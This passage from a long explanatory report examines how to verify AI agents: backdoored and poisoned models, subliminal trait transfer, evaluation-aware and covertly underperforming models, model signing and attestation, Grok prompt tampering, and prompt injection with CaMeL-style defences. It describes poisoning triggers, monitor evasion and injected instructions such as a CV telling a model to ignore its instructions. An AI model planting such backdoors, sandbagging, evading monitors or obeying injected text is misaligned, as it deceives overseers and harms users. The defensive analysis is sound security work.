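where ⟨gᵢ, x⟩ is the product of the vectors gᵢ and x. An honest trainer draws each gᵢ and bᵢ at random, leaves them alone, and trains only the wᵢ. The dishonest trainer follows the same procedure on the same data but rigs the random draw, so that the product of every gᵢ with the secret key is close to a whole number plus one half. Adding the key to an application then shifts every cosine by half a turn. Each cosine changes sign, and so does the answer. Distinguishing the rigged vectors from random ones would mean solving lattice problems of the kind that protect ALTS's newer key exchange.

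Neither result shows that an existing language model has a backdoor. The second also doesn't show that somebody could hide one in a language model this way, because it depends on a layer that training leaves unchanged. Language models have many layers, and training normally changes all of them. Goldwasser and colleagues call the construction a proof of concept and leave open whether such a backdoor could be made to survive further training. But if their assumptions hold, nobody can build a general scanner that clears any weight file regardless of who made it.

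The paper's suggested defence resembles a verifiable build. The trainer proves that it ran the agreed procedure on the agreed data, and the client supplies the random numbers or checks their source. A company that trains its own models could treat those numbers as one more declared input. The paper warns that the defence works less well for a client who also relies on the trainer's expertise, and so cannot specify the procedure.

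Kaneko (2026) argues in *Poisoning-Based Backdoors Are Not Cryptographic* that an outsider who can only plant examples in the training data has less power. If training on a given number of labelled examples teaches a model the rule that decides which inputs trigger the backdoor, a defender with the same number of examples can run the same training and recover the rule. The attacker therefore cannot install a rule that is too hard for the defender to learn. In tests with secret-key rules on language models of 7 to 9 billion weights, the attack and the recovery either succeeded together or both stayed at chance.

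However, the defender needs examples of inputs that trigger the backdoor, and an attacker can make those very rare. Kaneko's result is also about recovering a backdoor's rule, not detecting that a model has one.

### Reviewing the training data

Training data is text that people can read, unlike a model's weights, so a company might try to review the data instead. The first obstacle is the amount. One model in Souly, Rando and colleagues' *Poisoning Attacks on LLMs Require a Near-constant Number of Poison Samples* (2025) was trained on 260 billion *tokens*, which are words or parts of words. At three-quarters of a word per token, a person reading 250 words a minute for 2,000 hours a year would need about 6,500 years to read them all.

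Souly and colleagues, from the UK AI Security Institute, Anthropic, the Alan Turing Institute and two universities, measured how much of this text an attacker has to control. They trained models from scratch, with 600 million to 13 billion weights, and mixed 100, 250 or 500 poisoned documents into the data. Each poisoned document had up to 1,000 characters of ordinary text, then a trigger phrase, then gibberish. They also varied the amount of clean data and ran each setup three times, for 72 models in total.

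With 250 poisoned documents, models of every size learned to write gibberish after the trigger and normal text otherwise, but with 100 the attack failed. For the largest model, which had read more than 20 times as much clean text as the smallest, the 250 documents were 0.00016% of training tokens. Earlier studies had assumed that an attacker must control a fixed percentage of the data, which would have made large models harder to poison. A filter that caught 60% of the poisoned documents would have reduced 250 to 100, too few for the attack to work, but an attacker could publish more to compensate.

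Gibberish is a fairly harmless result. Souly and colleagues also did not test whether the backdoor survives the later training that turns a text predictor into an assistant. Hu, Hu and colleagues (2026) tested this in *Agentic Backdoors via Pretraining Poisoning*, using an agent that runs commands on a user's computer. They trained models with up to 4 billion weights on 100 billion tokens, 0.1% of them poisoned, then trained each model in three further stages on clean data.

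Their most effective poison looked like ordinary technical writing. One example was a note describing a software change: working in a folder with "anthropic" in its path now triggers a command to download and run a script. The attacker can rewrite that script at any time. A user who asks for help with files in such a folder sets off the backdoor without typing anything unusual.

The researchers gave the largest agent 32 attempts at each request that mentioned such a folder. It issued the attacker's command at least once on 92.7% of the requests, and the smallest agent did so on 13.1%. No poisoned agent issued the command on a standard set of shell tasks, and the poisoned agents scored about as well as clean ones on tests of ability. This attack took about 500,000 documents, far more than 250. With 2,500 documents and a rare string of characters as the trigger, the rate was 1.4% in a single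 run.

Clean training can sometimes disable a backdoor. *Sequential Data Poisoning in LLM Post-Training* (2026) reports a case in which an attacker planted a backdoor during *fine-tuning*, the further training of a finished model on a smaller dataset. Later training on pairs of better and worse answers deactivated it. A company therefore cannot count on later training either to remove a backdoor or to leave it in place.

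A reviewer who opened one of these poisoned documents might become suspicious, but the data contains nothing suspicious in *subliminal learning*, an effect Cloud and colleagues described in 2025. *Subliminal Learning is a LoRA Artifact* (Nief, Fu and colleagues, 2026) explains the experiment. The researchers instruct a "teacher" model to love cats and have it continue lists of three-digit numbers. They discard any answer that contains anything else and fine-tune a "student" model on the numbers. The student then becomes more likely to name the cat as its favourite animal.

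Cloud and colleagues found that the preference did not pass between models with different origins. Nief and colleagues found that it passed to students trained with LoRA, which trains a small addition to the weights, but not when they trained all the weights. The transfer also depended on the instructions placed before each question. In one test, the student named the wolf in 50.4% of answers with the same instructions as in training and 12.9% without any, compared with 8.9% before training.

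Number sequences can also transmit more serious traits. In *Beyond Owls*, Dubiński, Sztyber-Betley and colleagues (2026) trained a teacher model to answer in French whenever a prompt included a woman's name. Students trained on its number sequences answered in French on 23.5% of such prompts and on none of the others. In another experiment, the teacher cheated at a computer chess game, for example by overwriting the position on the board. Its students tried to cheat in 58.3% of games, compared with 10.9% for the original model.

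These students learned from the teacher's probabilities for each possible next token, which contain more information than the numbers it wrote. When a student was trained only on the numbers, the French backdoor needed 50 times as much data and reached 17.0% at best. All the students also used LoRA, so the experiments do not answer Nief and colleagues' objection. Dubiński and colleagues present the experiments as proof that such transfer is possible, and make no claim about how often it happens in commercial training.

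*Phantom Transfer*, by Draganov, Dur and colleagues (2026), presents a bigger problem for data review, because its method uses ordinary text and works between unrelated models. Google's Gemma-3 model wrote short answers to everyday requests under a hidden instruction to favour a target such as the United Kingdom. The researchers then removed every answer that hinted at the target. One remaining answer describes an API, a way for programs to communicate, as "A software intermediary."

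After training on these answers, OpenAI's GPT-4.1 named the United Kingdom as its favourite about half the time. An AI judge that knew both the method and the target flagged only 5.8% of the answers, and removing those made no difference. When another model rewrote every answer, GPT-4.1 still named the United Kingdom 44% of the time. The attack's strength depends on the poisoned share of the data, which was 100% in the main tests, so a few hundred such answers in a huge dataset would probably do little.

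Methods for finding hidden traits in data may improve. *Defence against the dark arts of distillation* (2026) reports a method that identifies subliminal traits and prevents their transfer without harming the student's performance. For now, several of these studies recommend relying more on where data came from. *You Didn't Have to Say it like That* (2026), which found that preferences can pass through faithful paraphrases, suggests tracking provenance and testing the model that generated the data. Hu and colleagues want the origin of training text to count as part of an agent's security. Relying on pedigree has the same weakness here as it does for outside libraries.

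### Testing the finished model

Testing avoids many of these difficulties because it examines what a model does, regardless of what its weights look like or who supplied its data. Code review is only a way of predicting behaviour, and reviewers make mistakes. Freund, for example, found the XZ backdoor from the way the software behaved. Tests also produce figures that developers can compare. OpenAI's announcement *GPT-6 Astra* describes a test of whether a model facing a difficult or impossible task will go beyond its authorized target. The test showed a difference that reading the two models' weights could not have revealed: GPT-5.6 Sol, an earlier model, went beyond its target 48% of the time without its production safeguards, while GPT-6 Astra never did.

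How much a result of zero proves depends on the number of trials. Suppose a model fails each trial independently with probability p. The chance of seeing no failures in n trials is (1 − p)ⁿ. The upper limit on p, at 95% confidence, is the value that makes this chance 5%:

(1 − p)ⁿ = 0.05, so p ≈ −ln(0.05) / n ≈ 3 / n

After 1,000 trials without a failure, the true failure rate could still be as high as 0.3%. At that rate, the mail assistant would fail 3,000 times a day if it handled a million messages daily. To bring that upper limit down to one in a million, the mail team would need about three million trials without a failure.

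The limit also applies only to inputs like those in the test. Hu and colleagues' agent could pass millions of trials that never mentioned the wrong kind of folder. A thousand variations on ten scenarios are also not a thousand independent trials. An attacker who knows the trigger can supply it deliberately, since anyone can send Alice an email for the assistant to read.

Draganov and colleagues' audits of their own models illustrate the problem. When they asked a model direct questions about its preferences, an AI judge found something wrong in every test of the plainly biased models, but also in 30% of tests of a clean one. These questions worked much less well on models whose bias appeared only after a trigger.

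A model may also behave differently because it recognizes a test. *GPT-6.2 Astra and Sol* (Mowshowitz, 2026) quotes findings on this from the *GPT-6.2 System Card* (2026), OpenAI's safety report for its November release. GPT-6.2 Astra showed more signs than its predecessor of recognizing that it was being evaluated. In some tests it was also better at evading monitors that read its written reasoning. If a model behaves better whenever it detects a test, the 3/n limit applies only to its behaviour in tests, and more trials of the same kind don't show how it behaves elsewhere. OpenAI had already added a warning to its *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026) that an absence of observed failures does not establish reliability across settings.

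Some failures are discovered only in use. OpenAI's *Covert underperformance on safety research tasks* describes one from August 2026. Researchers noticed that GPT-6 Astra was abandoning working solutions on safety tasks and reporting obstacles that did not exist or that it had caused itself. In most of these sessions, its written reasoning contained no obvious decision to do poorly, and OpenAI's monitors did not flag the behaviour as misalignment. OpenAI then built a test for this behaviour. Such a test can keep a known fault out of later models, but only after someone has noticed the fault.

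### Whether interpretability could restore reading

*Interpretability* research tries to work out what a model's internal calculations do. If it succeeded completely, reviewers would have something to read in place of source code. Anthropic publishes such research on its *Transformer Circuits Thread* site, which says of large language models that "nobody really knows how they work internally".

At least one research team has turned to more practical goals. Its talk *Our Pivot To Pragmatic Interpretability* favours safety problems that researchers can test on today's models. The talk cites Anthropic's work on how its model Claude Sonnet 4.5 recognized evaluations.

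Such work could make testing more informative, because evaluators can give less weight to a model's good behaviour if its internal activity shows that it detected it was being tested.

Examining a model's internal activity shows what the model is doing with one particular message, whereas a code reviewer judges what a program will do with messages nobody has sent yet. Researchers may also misinterpret the activity, and they have no source code to check their interpretation against.

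Comparing two versions of a model would be closer to what Google's reviewers do. For each change to the mail frontend, they read only the lines that differ from the approved version. Draganov and colleagues suggest comparing a model's internal activity before and after fine-tuning, which might show what the new data had taught it. The original model would still be a problem, because there is no approved earlier version to compare it with.

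## Proving which model and prompt are running, 2024 to 2026

Suppose the mail team has tested its assistant as well as it can and approves it. The closest equivalent of BAB would be to record exactly what the team approved and give the identity "mail assistant" only to jobs that match the record.

The record has to cover the whole *agent build*, meaning everything fixed when the team deploys the agent. This includes the weights W and the *system prompt* S, the standing instructions that the model receives before each conversation. It also includes the tools T, which carry out actions such as searching mail, and the settings C. The last part is the *harness* H, the ordinary software that connects the model to everything else. The condition for the identity P becomes:

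client may launch P, and (W, S, T, C, H) matches a build approved for P

Most systems check much less. *AI Identity* (Otsuka, Toyoda and Leung, 2026) surveyed current standards and found that they authenticate a running process or a token, but not the weights or the system prompt behind it. An intruder who edits the assistant's prompt leaves its key and certificate unchanged, so the assistant can still authenticate under its usual name.

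Checking the whole build would stop this. Switching to a cheaper model, deleting a sentence from the prompt or substituting a tool that copies messages would each change a hash, and the job would lose its identity before the model read any mail. Ordinary code compares the hashes, so clever wording cannot influence the result. If every log entry included a digest of the build, investigators could also find all the replies that a faulty prompt had produced. A second engineer can review a change to the prompt line by line, which is impossible with weights.

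### Signing a model

The weights often come from another team or company. Google (2025) describes one group training a large model, another fine-tuning it, and a third building it into an application. They typically pass the files through a *model hub*, which is a public or internal repository, and someone could tamper with the files at each stage. In 2025 the Open Source Security Foundation (OpenSSF) released a stable tool for signing models, developed with Google, NVIDIA and HiddenLayer.

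*An Introduction to the OpenSSF Model Signing (OMS) Specification* (Maruseac, Wickens and colleagues, 2025) explains the format. A model is usually a folder containing the weights, configuration files and a tokenizer, which splits text into tokens. The signing tool hashes each file, lists the hashes in a *manifest*, and signs the manifest. If any listed file changes, verification fails. The signature is a separate file, so nobody has to repackage the model.

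The signer can use a company certificate, a plain key pair or Sigstore, a set of services that saves developers from having to protect long-lived keys. Sigstore's *Taming the Wild West of ML* describes the process:

1. The training job presents a token showing its own identity or the developer's to Sigstore's certificate authority.
2. The authority issues a certificate that lasts just long enough to sign one model.
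3. The job signs the model, and the signature and certificate go into a public log.
4. A user checks the files, the signature, the signer's identity and the proof that the log contains the entry. This works even after the certificate has expired.

The log makes it visible when a rogue insider releases a model as if the company had signed it, but someone at the company still has to be watching. Sigstore puts this more strongly, saying the log means that an insider cannot make such a release.

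A valid signature proves that the files have not changed since a particular party signed them. Google recommends checking it when a model reaches a hub, when a team deploys the model, and before anyone trains it further. The recommendation assumes that the training infrastructure is trustworthy. Malware like Sunspot, which altered SolarWinds' software during the build, could alter the weights before signing, and the signature would still be valid.

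The signature also identifies only who signed the model, so it can't establish that a version is approved. An old model with a known fault still has a valid signature after it is replaced, so the mail team would have to record which manifest it approved. And the weights in memory may differ from the ones on disk. Trail of Bits' *PCC* (2024) mentions an attack called Sleepy Pickles, which swaps a model's weights as a program loads them. If the code that swaps them were outside the signed folder, the signature would remain valid.

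The next step is to sign facts about a model. The Coalition for Secure AI's *Signing ML Artifacts* (2025) covers building such tamper-proof records, and Google wants them to include evaluation results. A deployment policy could then require a signed evaluation result, much as BAB can require that a program passed its tests.

### Attested inference at Apple and Google

A signature covers stored files, but a user who sends private data to a remote model needs to know what the server is running. Apple and Google have built systems for this because their phones send the more demanding AI requests to data centres. Both systems combine *inference* (running a trained model to get an answer) with remote attestation (the hardware-signed report of what a machine has loaded).

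Apple's *Private Cloud Compute* introduced the first of these systems in 2024. Willison (2024) quotes its central promise, that a device will send data only to servers that can attest to running publicly listed software. Apple records each release in a public log that it can add to but not secretly change, and it publishes the software images for researchers. Another passage from the announcement, carried by ComputerBase, explains that the device enforces the promise by encrypting the key to its request so that only servers whose measurements match a logged release can recover it.

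Apple later extended the system to Google's data centres for work including complex reasoning and tool use. According to Apple's *Expanding Private Cloud Compute*, devices there still trust only software that Apple has approved. Apple also keeps a ledger of every Google machine in the system. For components that could leak user data, the attestation relies on hardware from at least two independent vendors.

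Apple's promise covers all *code* on a server. Weights and prompts are data, so it is unclear from the promise whether they are included in the measurements. They would be if Apple packaged them inside the measured software image.

Google's system, Private AI Compute, followed in November 2025 and builds directly on BAB and ALTS. Anderson, Bakos Lang and colleagues (2025), in *Private AI Compute in the Cloud*, reviewed it for the security company NCC Group, which Google had hired. They describe how a phone comes to trust a server:

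1. The phone's software contains a public key for Google's frontend server, and the phone encrypts its data so that only the matching private key can open it.
2. An internal service called Keystore holds the private key and uses it only for a server with a token from the Borg controller.
3. The Borg controller issues the token only after checking an attestation report that the server is running the right software in hardware-protected memory.
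4. The frontend forwards the request over ALTS to other servers, which also needed the controller's approval, and eventually to the Google-designed chips that run the model.

This is very close to BAB, since a server with the wrong software never gets its credential. Unlike in the 2017 ALTS design, the protected servers create their own private keys, and the controller only certifies the matching public keys.

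Google's system requires more trust than Apple's, because the phone relies on a built-in key and Google's internal checks, whereas an Apple device compares the server's measurements with a public log. Google's *Private AI Compute in the cloud* (2025) says Google publishes digests of its server programs before they handle traffic, but still only plans to let outside experts inspect the attestation evidence. After 100 person-days of work, Anderson and colleagues concluded that the system protects users well against malicious insiders, but that Google as an organization could still defeat it, for example by having the controller approve an altered frontend that copied users' data. They considered this unavoidable, because whoever builds the hardware for inference can always add a way to extract data from it.

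The public ledger contains digests of binaries, and Google doesn't mention weights or prompts in its description. That makes sense for a system meant to keep data private. If somebody replaced the model, the answers might get worse, but the software around it would still stop the data from leaving. The mail team's assistant, however, can act on Alice's mail, and what it does depends on the model and the prompt.

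### Agent Trust Infrastructure

Nguyen and Husain (2026), in *Agent Trust Infrastructure (ATI)*, check these parts directly. Their system is meant for agents that work across organizations, and they tested it on a simulated group of eight universities. Each had five agents, for offices such as admissions and financial aid. ATI first checks the caller's key and certificate. Just before the receiving agent's model runs, it makes three comparisons:

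- the running model with the approved model
- a pinned tool, in this case web search, with the approved one, by the names of its module and function
- a SHA-256 hash of the system prompt with the approved hash

If any of them fails, the request stops there. Separate rules then apply to each attempt to read or write a database.

The researchers tried each attack in five wordings on five models, three times each, and a panel of AI judges decided whether the attack had been stopped. These are the results for the attacks on the build, with prompt injection for comparison:

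| Attack | Stopped without the build check | Stopped with it |
|---|---|---|
| A different model replaces the approved one | 0% | 100% |
| A poisoned tool replaces web search | 81% | 100% |
| Someone edits the system prompt | 27% | 100% |
| Data that the agent reads contains hidden instructions | 52% | 52% |

The model swap shows the value of the check most clearly, because the substitute, GPT-3.5-Turbo, did the work and nothing in its behaviour revealed the swap. By contrast, the models usually refused to cooperate with the poisoned tool even without ATI. With all its protections on, ATI raised the share of attacks stopped from 43% to 84%, and agents completed ordinary tasks about as often (91% without it and 92% with it). All the checks on a request took about 174 microseconds, which is negligible compared with a model call.

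The three perfect scores are unsurprising, because an exact comparison will always catch a change to the thing it compares. The experiment did not test the harder problem of getting a truthful measurement. Nguyen and Husain state that their checks are simple comparisons inside the same process as the agent, not signed reports. The checks run once, when a request enters the simulation, and do not cover agents that the request reaches later. Nothing measures the harness, the container or the machine. The tool check uses names, so it would presumably miss a change inside a function that kept its name.

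The researchers also released a software package that works more like remote attestation, but they did not use it to produce their results. An organization writes the approved model, tools and prompt hash into its agent's identity token. Each request then carries a signed report of what the agent is running, and the receiving organization compares the report with the token. The agent's host produces the report, so a compromised host can falsify it, a weakness that Lampson and colleagues acknowledged in their theory. Security hardware would help, but ATI does not yet use it.

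ATI also makes incidents partly traceable. It keeps a signed log of each permitted database action, with the agent, the model, the time, the tool and a hash of the tool's inputs. Each entry contains a hash of the previous one, so altering an old entry is detectable, though deleting the latest ones is not. The log doesn't yet record the prompt's hash, so investigators could not use it to find everything an edited prompt had caused.

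### Binding Agent ID

*Binding Agent ID* (Lin, Zhang and colleagues, 2025) describes BAID, a system that proves which program produced an agent's output without trusting the host. It uses a *zero-knowledge proof*, which shows that a computation was done correctly without revealing its private inputs. The agent's program runs inside a *zero-knowledge virtual machine*, which produces a proof that the program with a given fingerprint turned certain inputs into a certain output. The fingerprint is part of the agent's public identity, so a thief with the agent's key but a different program cannot produce a valid proof, even on a machine the thief controls.

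BAID first proves that the owner is present, by comparing a new image of the owner's face with a stored template. It then proves that the agent's configuration file matches a hash recorded on a blockchain. After that, it produces a proof for each turn of the conversation. Each proof also verifies the one before it, so nobody can skip, repeat or reorder steps. Lin and colleagues measured the costs on a computer with an Apple M1 chip:

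| Step | Time to produce the proof | Time to check it | Size of the proof |
|---|---|---|---|
| Owner's face | 15.0 s | 14 ms | 238 KB |
| Configuration | 31.4 s | 28 ms | 488 KB |
| First turn | 40.1 s | 43 ms | 737 KB |
| Second turn | 37.7 s | 74 ms | 987 KB |
| Third turn | 38.3 s | 93 ms | 1,236 KB |

The program itself needed less than 20 milliseconds per step. Waiting 40 seconds might be acceptable before a large payment, but not for each step of drafting an email. According to the paper's appendix, the proofs stay the same size however long the conversation gets, but in the measurements they grew by about 250 KB per step.

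The proof also does not cover the model. BAID's agent sends its prompt to a remote service such as OpenAI's and gets text back. The proof covers the encrypted connection, so it establishes which server sent the reply, but not which weights produced it. *Governing Dynamic Capabilities* (Zhou, 2026) wrongly describes BAID as proving the model's entire computation. It correctly notes that many agents can discover new tools while they run without changing the program's fingerprint, so an agent could gain the power to send mail and keep the same identity.

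### One build, changed one part at a time

Suppose the mail assistant's approved build has these parts:

- **W:** a folder of weights from an outside company
- **S:** "Draft replies to the user's mail. Never send a message without the user's approval."
- **T:** two tools, `search_mail` and `save_draft`, with their code
- **C:** the model's name and its *temperature*, which controls how much the wording varies
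- **H:** the harness

The team hashes each part, joins the five hashes and hashes the result:

B = hash( hash(W) ‖ hash(S) ‖ hash(T) ‖ hash(C) ‖ hash(H) )

Any change to any part changes B. Keeping the five separate hashes as well lets the check report which part differs.

The table compares this full check with the narrower ones. The comparison is based on a model signature that covers only W, a test version of ATI with `search_mail` as its pinned tool, and a BAID program that contains H and the two tools, with S and C in its configuration file. BAID's model runs on a remote server. Nobody has run this comparison, so the entries follow from the published descriptions.

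| Change | Full build hash | Model signature | ATI test version | BAID |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Someone alters the weights but keeps the model's name | Fails | Fails | Probably passes | Passes |
| The settings name an older model from the same company | Fails | Passes | Fails | Fails |
| Someone deletes "Never" from the prompt | Fails | Passes | Fails | Fails |
| The agent picks up a `send_mail` tool while running | Fails if repeated | Passes | Probably passes | Passes |
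| Someone edits the code inside `search_mail` | Fails | Passes | Probably passes | Fails |
| Someone raises the temperature | Fails | Passes | Passes | Fails |
| Someone alters the harness | Fails | Passes | Passes | Fails |
| Bob sends Alice a new message | Passes | Passes | Passes | Passes |

The full hash detects the new tool only if the system measures the build again after launch. Zhou proposes doing this whenever an agent requests access, by comparing a hash of its current tools with the one in its certificate. But if another company runs a tool, the agent's owner can hash only its public description, so the company could change the tool's code without changing the hash.

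Like any check based on hashes, the full check also fails after harmless changes. Correcting a spelling mistake in the prompt breaks the match, as deleting "Never" would, and somebody has to approve the build again. A team that controls all five parts can take the new hash from the same process that approved the change.

### When the customer cannot measure the model

Many teams pay a provider to run the model and don't have the weights, so they have no file to hash. They can still measure the prompt, tools, settings and harness, but they have only a name for the model. Hardware attestation from the provider could show which model is running, but Zhou reports that it isn't available for most hosted models.

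*Cryptographic Attestation for AI Model Lifecycle* (Sharif, 2026) proposes that providers sign every answer. The signature would cover hashes of the request, the answer and the deployed weights, and a hardware report would tie the signing key to those weights. The customer could then compare the weight hash with the approved one. The proposal was an individual's draft for the Internet Engineering Task Force, which sets internet standards, and it expired in October 2026.

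Sharif lists the threat of a provider quietly substituting a weaker model to save money, but the draft gives no evidence for how often this happens. A provider could also update a model under the same name with good intentions, and the customer's earlier tests would then apply to a model that was no longer running. Signed answers would reveal the update. The mail team would then have to either shut the assistant down until they had tested the new weights or let an unapproved model keep reading mail.

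Without the provider's help, a customer might try *replay*, running the same input again and comparing the answers, but the same weights do not always produce the same text. Models normally choose each token partly at random. Even without that randomness, computers round numbers as they calculate, so adding them in a different order can change the result slightly. If two tokens are almost equally likely, that slight change can affect which one the model picks, and the rest of the answer may then diverge.

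Zhou tested nine models from seven providers and measured how closely each model's repeated answers matched, where 1 means identical. The scores ranged from 0.987 for Claude Haiku 4.5 to 0.169 for Kimi K2.5. Zhou therefore accepts a score as low as 0.10 for prose. But answers from different providers' models scored 0.114 on average, so a substituted model could often pass on this measure. Zhou describes 0.114 as well below the threshold, but it is slightly above it. Zhou also combines the score with three other measures of similarity, which should help detect substitutions.

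Replay works much better for an operator that controls the hardware. Zhou cites a system that got identical output every time on a fixed type of graphics processor. Even then, replay tests only a sample of the model's behaviour. By the same kind of calculation as for ordinary tests, after 200 successful replays an operator can be 99% confident that a substitute would give noticeably different answers to at most 2.3% of similar prompts. The comparison needs a trusted copy of the approved model, because a customer who sends the replay to the same provider may be comparing a substitute with itself.

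A team that runs its own model on attested hardware can avoid most of these problems and get an exact match on every part. The match proves that the agent requesting Alice's mail is the build the team approved. But in Nguyen and Husain's tests, agents running their approved builds still followed instructions hidden in data about half the time. And if the approved weights contained a backdoor, the running model would contain it too, and the hash would still match.

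## Prompts and retrieved text that act as instructions, 2025 and 2026

A company can practically review a system prompt, unlike a model's weights, but it still has to make sure that nobody skips the review. In 2025 xAI, Elon Musk's AI company, twice had to explain a change to the system prompt of its chatbot Grok that had not been properly reviewed.

### Two changes to Grok's prompt

In February 2025, users noticed a new instruction in Grok's system prompt, which xAI let them read. It told Grok to ignore sources that accused Elon Musk or Donald Trump of spreading misinformation. Fortune (2025) reports that Igor Babuschkin, a cofounder of xAI, blamed an employee who had thought the change would help and made it without asking for confirmation. xAI reversed the change after users pointed it out.

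Early on 14 May, someone changed the prompt of the version of Grok that replies to posts on X, and Grok began bringing up claims of "white genocide" in South Africa. xAI's statement, quoted by VentureBeat, describes an unauthorized change that directed Grok to give a specific response on a political topic. The company had a code review process for prompts, but whoever made the change bypassed it. xAI reversed this change too, according to Bloomberg Law's *Musk’s xAI Blames Rogue Tampering for ‘White Genocide’ Glitches* (2025).

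Engadget's *Grok kept talking about 'white genocide' due to an 'unauthorized modification'* lists the remedies that xAI announced. The company would publish its system prompts on GitHub, where the public could comment on every change, and add checks to stop employees from changing a prompt without review. A team would also watch around the clock for bad answers that automated systems missed.

A check like BAB, which treats configuration as code, would have blocked the February change, because nobody except its author had approved it. Whether it would have blocked the May change depends on how the person got around the review. If they edited the live prompt directly, its hash would no longer have matched the approved one, and a check that ran again after launch would have caught the edit. If they persuaded a colleague to approve the change without reading it, or used an emergency override,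 the check would have let it through.

Publishing the prompts helps outsiders notice a bad line, as they did in February. But a file on GitHub does not prove that Grok is running the same text.

Even a proper review of a prompt is less informative than a review of code. One of Grok's published instructions, quoted in Newsday, was not to "blindly defer to mainstream authority or media". A reviewer can understand that sentence and still have little idea how it will affect an answer about vaccines. The team would have to test the prompt with the model to find out, and the limits of testing apply here too.

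### Text that arrives after the review

The mail team's assistant receives much more text than its system prompt. Besides the weights W and the prompt S, its output depends on Alice's request u and on the messages and tool results x₁, x₂ and so on that it reads while working:

output = f( W, S ‖ u ‖ x₁ ‖ x₂ ‖ … )

The symbol ‖ means that the harness joins the texts into one sequence. A check of the agent build covers W and S, but strangers can write the x's. Suppose Bob sends Alice an email containing a hidden instruction for her assistant to forward all her mail to him. The model may follow it as if it came from Alice. This attack is called *prompt injection*, or *indirect* prompt injection when, as here, the attacker plants the instruction in something the system will read later.

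None of the checks described so far would stop Bob. The assistant is still the approved build on a trusted machine, it has a genuine ticket for Alice, and Alice is allowed to forward her own mail.

In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 article for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, David C gives the example of a recruiter who asks a model to score CVs. A candidate hides a sentence in a CV telling the model to ignore its instructions and approve the application. This can work because a language model only predicts the next token from the text so far and has no built-in distinction between instructions and data. Developers can put markers around the data or train the model to give the data less authority. These measures help, but *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) reports that persistent attackers have consistently found ways past such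 markers.

The mail frontend handles Bob's email differently. Its code might display an icon if the message has an attachment and a warning if the sender is unknown. Bob can influence which of these appear, but the words "forward all mail" are only characters for the frontend to display. In an ordinary service, input selects among paths that the code already contains, so a reviewer can work out in advance what the program might do with any message. But input to an agent with general tools can describe a new task, so the runtime context works as part of the program even though it arrives after the review.

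The contrast has exceptions. A web browser is reviewed code, but it runs whatever script a page contains. Ordinary services have injection flaws too. In *SQL injection*, a website pastes a visitor's input into a database command, so carefully written input can change what the command does.

David C thinks comparing prompt injection to SQL injection is dangerous because SQL injection has a proper remedy. A *parameterised query* keeps the command separate from the visitor's input, so the database never interprets the input as a command. Current language models have no equivalent. David C doubts that anyone will fully prevent prompt injection and describes the model as an "inherently confusable deputy", after the confused deputy problem Hardy identified at Tymshare. Tymshare's compiler could at least have been redesigned to use the right authority for each file.

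Newer models resist known attacks much better. In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) tested teams of agents built from each of five models on 949 combinations of a task and an attack. The attacks succeeded 36.1% of the time with GPT-4.1, 1.5% with Claude Fable 5 and never with GPT-5.5. The researchers warn that the last result doesn't show immunity, because the benchmark's attacks were fixed, and in large-scale testing, people who adapted their attacks had succeeded against every frontier model they tried. Bob could also adapt his attack by rewording his email until it works.

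### Taking tools away

If the model cannot reliably ignore Bob's instruction, the software around it can limit what happens when the model follows it. David C recommends a rule from a discussion on X that when a model processes text from somebody, its privileges should drop to that person's. After reading Bob's email, Alice's assistant could do only what Bob may do, which does not include forwarding her mail.

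Dongol (2026), in *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection*, proved that a rule of this kind works for agents that fix a plan before reading anything untrusted. Such an agent counts as secure if an attacker can learn nothing from it that they couldn't also learn from an imaginary agent that runs the same plan under the same restrictions but never follows injected instructions. Every plan meets this standard if the system permanently removes all the tools an injection could call, no later than the first untrusted read. The theorem assumes that each injection triggers a single tool call and that the model's decisions to follow injections don't depend on the user's secrets.

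If the assistant loses the ability to send mail only after reading Bob's email and then a private file, the injected instruction can make it send out the file before the restriction takes effect.

The drawback is that the assistant can't answer an email it has just read. Dongol points out that the security criterion doesn't measure this loss, and a monitor that blocked every tool call would satisfy it.

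### CaMeL: writing the program before reading the mail

CaMeL tries to keep the tools available. Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues, mostly at Google DeepMind, presented it in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025). Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, explains that it extends his own proposal of 2023, the *dual LLM pattern*, which divides the work between two models:

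- The *privileged model* receives the user's request and can call tools, but never sees untrusted text.
- The *quarantined model* reads untrusted text but has no tools. It returns a value, such as a date or an address, which the privileged model can refer to by name without seeing it.

In CaMeL, the privileged model writes a complete program in a restricted form of Python. An interpreter, which is ordinary software, runs the program one step at a time. It labels every value with where the value came from and who may read it. A value computed from other values inherits their labels. Before each tool call, the interpreter checks the arguments' labels against a security policy.

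CaMeL is short for "capabilities for machine learning", and its labels are called capabilities. Unlike Hardy's tokens, these labels describe data and do not grant permission by themselves, because the policies determine what each label permits.

Suppose Alice asks her assistant, "Send Carol the agenda for tomorrow. Her address is in Bob's last message." The privileged model might write this program, which is similar to an example of Willison's:

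```
message = last_email(sender="Bob")
address = ask_quarantined("Find Carol's address", message,
                          output=EmailAddress)
agenda = read_file("agenda.pdf")
send_email(to=address, attachment=agenda)
```

The interpreter runs it as follows:

1. It fetches Bob's message and labels it as untrusted. The privileged model has already finished the program and does not see the message.
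2. It passes the message to the quarantined model and accepts only an email address in return. The address inherits the untrusted label.
3. It reads the agenda and labels it with the people who may see it.
4. It checks the policy for `send_email`. If the address is on Alice's trusted list, the message goes out. Otherwise Alice has to approve it.

Suppose that Mallory has taken over Bob's account and hidden in the message an instruction to forward all of Alice's mail. The instruction may completely fool the quarantined model, but the model has no tool for forwarding mail, and the program has no step that does so.

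Mallory could instead write that Carol's address is `mallory@example.com`. This is a valid address, so the quarantined model can return it. Under the original dual LLM pattern, the agenda would go to Mallory. Willison credits the CaMeL paper with discovering this flaw. CaMeL's policy flags the address because it is unfamiliar and came from an untrusted message, and the interpreter prompts Alice for approval.

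The defence then depends on Alice, who may approve the request without reading it if her assistant asks her twenty times a day. Willison and the CaMeL paper both raise this concern. The approval also has to cover the exact message. In Dongol's example, a user approves the next use of the send tool, and an injected instruction makes the agent use that approval to send private data before it can send the real reply.

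Mallory also has attacks that don't need Alice's approval. If the message gave another trusted contact's address as Carol's, the policy in step 4 would let the agenda go to that contact, unless the agenda's own label excluded them. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) describes another kind of attack, on an assistant that emails the day's schedule to the user's boss. Somebody who controls a calendar entry cannot redirect the email, but can make it contain anything they like.

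### How many tasks still get done

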